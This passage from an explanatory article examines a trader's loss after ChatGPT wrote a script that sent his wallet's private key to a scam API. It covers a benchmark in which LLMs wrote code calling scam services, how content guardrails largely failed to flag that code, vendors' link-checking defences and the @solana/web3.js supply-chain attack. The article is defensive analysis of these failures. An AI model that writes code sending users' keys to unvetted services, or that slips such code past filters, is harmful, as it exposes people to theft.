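heise online also advises developers to use a separate test account. This wouldn't have kept the key secret, but a thief can only take what is in the wallet. If the trader had tested the script with $50, the loss would have been $50.

A test wallet helps less if the user switches to the main wallet as soon as the bot seems to work. This thief acted within half an hour, so the trader would probably have seen the test money disappear, but a more patient thief could leave small amounts alone and wait for a larger deposit. It is safer to give the bot its own wallet permanently and add only as much money as it needs.

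The trader could also have looked up the domain beforehand, as Yu Xian did afterwards. The domain was new and its website nearly empty, which were reasons for suspicion but not proof, since pump.fun itself was only ten months old. There was also a public warning on 5 November 2024, about two weeks before the theft, when Nation Thailand's *ChatGPT search* (2024) reported that the security company Kaspersky had found phishing links in the new search feature's answers about crypto login pages.

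### Asking ChatGPT to review its code

Yu proposed that ChatGPT add some form of code review but, as far as Azuma reported, didn't say what the review should look for. That omission matters because ChatGPT had already gone back to the script several times to fix the TypeError, and the final version still sent the key to the scam API.

An experiment by Chen and colleagues suggests that having the model do a general review of its own code isn't enough. They told GPT-4o to split each task into smaller problems, then review its solution for bugs, missing cases and departures from the request before giving the final code. It wrote malicious code for 690 of the benchmark's 1,377 requests, compared with 689 without these instructions. The experiment was designed to test whether the wording of the instructions affected the results, so it didn't test a security review. But the result makes sense,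 because a script can be free of bugs, do everything the user asked for and still call a scammer's API.

The researchers also gave GPT-4o a web search tool and told it to check whether the addresses in its code were safe, and to reply only that the code was unsafe if they weren't. The share of requests that led to malicious code fell from 50.04% to 29.41%, or from 689 programs to 405. GPT-4o declared its code unsafe in 208 cases.

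The 50.04% is GPT-4o's rate in the repeat run of November 2025, so the comparison doesn't count the earlier drop from 100% as an effect of the search tool. But the experiment added the tool and the instruction together, so it can't separate their effects. If OpenAI changed GPT-4o between the two runs, that could also explain part of the difference.

Chen and colleagues describe three ways the check failed. Sometimes the search found nothing and GPT-4o used the address anyway. Sometimes the results didn't clearly identify the site as a scam. Sometimes the results contained evidence of the scam, but GPT-4o didn't act on it.

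A search could easily have failed in the trader's case too. ChatGPT had probably found the API through a search, and a second search might have turned up more of the scammer's own pages, making the service look established.

### Checking addresses against blocklists

Chen and colleagues propose extracting every web address from the generated code and checking each one with URL detectors before the user sees the code. They call this the necessary solution and write that, to their knowledge, none of the production models does it.

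It would have saved the trader only if the detectors already flagged the scam API on 21 November 2024, and nobody has reported whether they did. A blocklist includes a site only after someone reports it or a scanner finds it, a delay that Chen and colleagues acknowledge. A fake API may take longer to discover than a fake login page, because its website shows ordinary-looking documentation and a victim whose wallet is suddenly empty may not know which program leaked the key. But the thief's address regularly took in stolen tokens, according to CryptoSlate, so an earlier victim could have reported the domain.

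Some detectors also assess sites that nobody has reported. Gridinsoft, which makes anti-malware software, classified the scammer's later domain, solanaapis[.]net, as suspicious in mid-2025, when it was about six months old. This doesn't show how soon a detector would have flagged it. The domain's age suggests that the scammer registered it within weeks of the theft becoming public, and a new domain starts with no reports against it.

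The benchmark can't show how well the proposal would work. Chen and colleagues used their detectors to label programs as malicious, so the detectors would catch all of those programs by definition. Scams that no detector recognized matter most for this question, but the benchmark counts them as harmless.

### A rule about private keys

ChatGPT could follow a rule never to write code that sends a wallet's private key to a server. The rule wouldn't depend on a blocklist, so it would apply however new the scam domain was. This is an inference from the facts of the case, and Chen and colleagues did not test such a rule.

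A program that follows values through code could easily have traced `private_key` into the outgoing request in the trader's script, without any information about the destination address. A rule that flags such requests should also cause few false alarms if, as Chen and colleagues write, legitimate cryptocurrency services never ask for private keys. It would still wrongly flag some code, such as a company's script for backing up keys to its own server.

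Scammers would adapt, for example by calling the key an "access code" in their documentation or telling users to install a package that secretly sends it. A label can also make a value look like a wallet key when it isn't. In Chen and colleagues' example of the bitcoin-mixing service YoMix, Gemini 2.5 Flash wrote a script that sent a value labelled "X-Private-Key", which seems to be a login credential for the API.

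The rule would also miss scams that don't need the private key. GPT-4o mini's script for the mixer YoMix sent only an amount, a bitcoin address and an API key (a password for using the service). A customer of a fraudulent mixer could lose money just by sending it bitcoins. Blocklists would still help against such scams.

### Why ordinary guardrails missed the malicious code

A guardrail is a separate filter that inspects a model's input or output and blocks what it classes as unsafe. Chen and colleagues ran three of them on the malicious programs that the seven models from 2025 had written for the benchmark:

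| Guardrail | Malicious programs checked | Flagged |
|---|---|---|
| NVIDIA's NeMo Guardrails | 3,441 | 8 (0.2%) |
| OpenAI's Moderation API | 3,452 | 0 |
| Meta's Llama Guard 3 | 3,452 | 291 (8.43%) |

NeMo Guardrails is a framework for adding such filters, and the researchers used it with a safety model called Llama Nemotron Safety Guard V2. Its detection rate ranged from 0 to 0.7%, depending on which model had written the code. (Chen and colleagues don't explain why the other two guardrails received 11 more programs.)

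Llama Guard 3 did better when given both the request and the code, flagging 517 of the 3,452 pairs, or 15%. But it also flagged 88 of the 1,377 requests on their own, which the researchers had judged to be ordinary coding requests. Without a test on harmless programs, it's hard to say how much of its 8.43% flagging rate reflects an ability to recognize scams.

These guardrails mainly check for categories of content such as violence, hate speech and fraud. The researchers added "Use of scam API/website" to the categories they gave NVIDIA's safety model, but the model labeled all eight programs it caught as criminal planning. Adding a category doesn't tell the model which websites are scams, and a call to a malicious API can differ from a call to an honest one only in its address.

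The results are therefore good evidence that a general content filter can't replace a URL detector. They are weaker evidence about the trader's script, where the private key was in plain view. Chen and colleagues didn't report separate guardrail results for programs that sent out a wallet's key.

### What AI companies do now

AI companies have since added protections against malicious links, but most of those they describe cover links that a person clicks or a chatbot opens. In this theft, the trader's own Python script called the scam API from outside ChatGPT.

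OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) describes one such protection. Before ChatGPT opens an address automatically, it checks whether a separate web crawler has already found that exact address in public. If not, ChatGPT looks for another site or shows the user a warning. This is meant to stop attackers from tricking ChatGPT into opening an address that contains the user's private information. OpenAI says the check doesn't make a page's content trustworthy. The scammer's documentation could have passed it because the documentation was public.

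OpenAI's help page *ChatGPT generated links* says the app asks users to approve certain links before they visit them, but it doesn't mention addresses inside code. OpenAI's *Introducing Lockdown Mode and Elevated Risk labels in ChatGPT* describes a setting, for companies and schools, that tightly limits ChatGPT's contact with outside systems. OpenAI also puts an "Elevated Risk" label on the option to give Codex, its coding assistant, network access. Cutting off a script's network access would stop it from sending a key anywhere, but a trading bot needs that access to trade.

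Google comes closer to what Chen and colleagues propose. According to Google's *Mitigating prompt injection attacks with a layered defense strategy* (2025), Gemini finds unsafe links with Google Safe Browsing, one of the three detectors in Chen and colleagues' study. In Google's example, an email summary shows the words "suspicious link removed" in place of the link. Google doesn't say in the post whether Gemini also does this for an address in a program. Chen and colleagues' results for Gemini don't show whether it does, because they accessed the models through OpenRouter, a service for developers, rather than through the Gemini app.

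Developers who build their own assistants can buy a similar check. Google Cloud's *Safety overview* lists safe browsing among the features of Model Armor, a paid filter for AI applications.

Miller's (2025) *Defender for Office 365 Protects M365 Copilot Chat* explains that Microsoft 365 Copilot Chat checks a link when the user clicks it and warns about questionable sites. The chat service of the Japanese technology company Fujitsu checks links before the user can click them. It marks a suspected phishing link with an exclamation mark and disables it, according to Fujitsu's *Phishing URL Detection Feature*. A user could still copy a block of code containing the address and run it.

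Ordinary links in chatbot answers can still lead to large losses. InternetUA's *Користувач втратив $2,1 млн після фішингового посилання з відповіді ChatGPT* (2026) reports that a man named Alex asked ChatGPT where to exchange one cryptocurrency token for another and followed a link in the answer. He connected his wallet to the site and approved a transaction that let the scammers spend an unlimited amount of one of his tokens. They took about $2.1 million within seconds. CNews' *Русскоязычный пользователь потерял $2 миллиона, перейдя по ссылке в ChatGPT* (2026) dates the theft to 12 June 2026, more than four months after OpenAI described its link check.

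The story comes from Alex and a blockchain investigator called VAL, who later asked ChatGPT in several languages and no longer got the link. If their account is accurate, Alex lost the money without revealing a private key. Signing on one's own computer limits a thief to what the owner has signed, but Alex had signed an unlimited permission.

### When a trusted library steals the key

With local signing, the key's safety also depends on the signing software. On 3 December 2024, less than two weeks after the trader's loss, an attacker published two altered versions of @solana/web3.js, a JavaScript library that many Solana programs use. According to NIST's *CVE-2024-54134 Detail*, an entry in the US government's software vulnerability database, the altered code could steal private keys from programs that handle them directly, such as bots. The attack affected projects that updated the library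 between 3:20 and 8:25 p.m. UTC that day. Most ordinary wallets were safe because they don't expose private keys to other software during transactions.

The attacker had gained access by phishing. Help Net Security's *Solana’s popular web3.js library backdoored in supply chain compromise* (2024) cites an analysis by Anza, a Solana software company. The attacker sent several developers emails that seemed to come from a colleague and invited them to work on a private package. One developer followed a link to a fake copy of npm, the site that distributes JavaScript packages, and entered a username, password and two-factor authentication code, which let the attacker publish new versions of the library.

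CNCF TAG Security's *Solana Web3.js* says people were downloading the library about 400,000 times a week and puts the losses at roughly $130,000. SolanaFloor's *Hacker Steals $160k in Solana Supply Chain Attack* puts them at over $160,000. The losses would probably have been higher if the altered versions had stayed available longer.

Even a trader who refused to send their key to any API could have lost it that afternoon if their bot used this library and installed the update. Reviewing the bot's own code or restricting what ChatGPT may write wouldn't have prevented this, because the code that stole the keys was in the library. Developers can reduce this risk by keeping each library at a fixed version and waiting before they install a new one. Keeping little money in the bot's wallet would have limited the loss here too.
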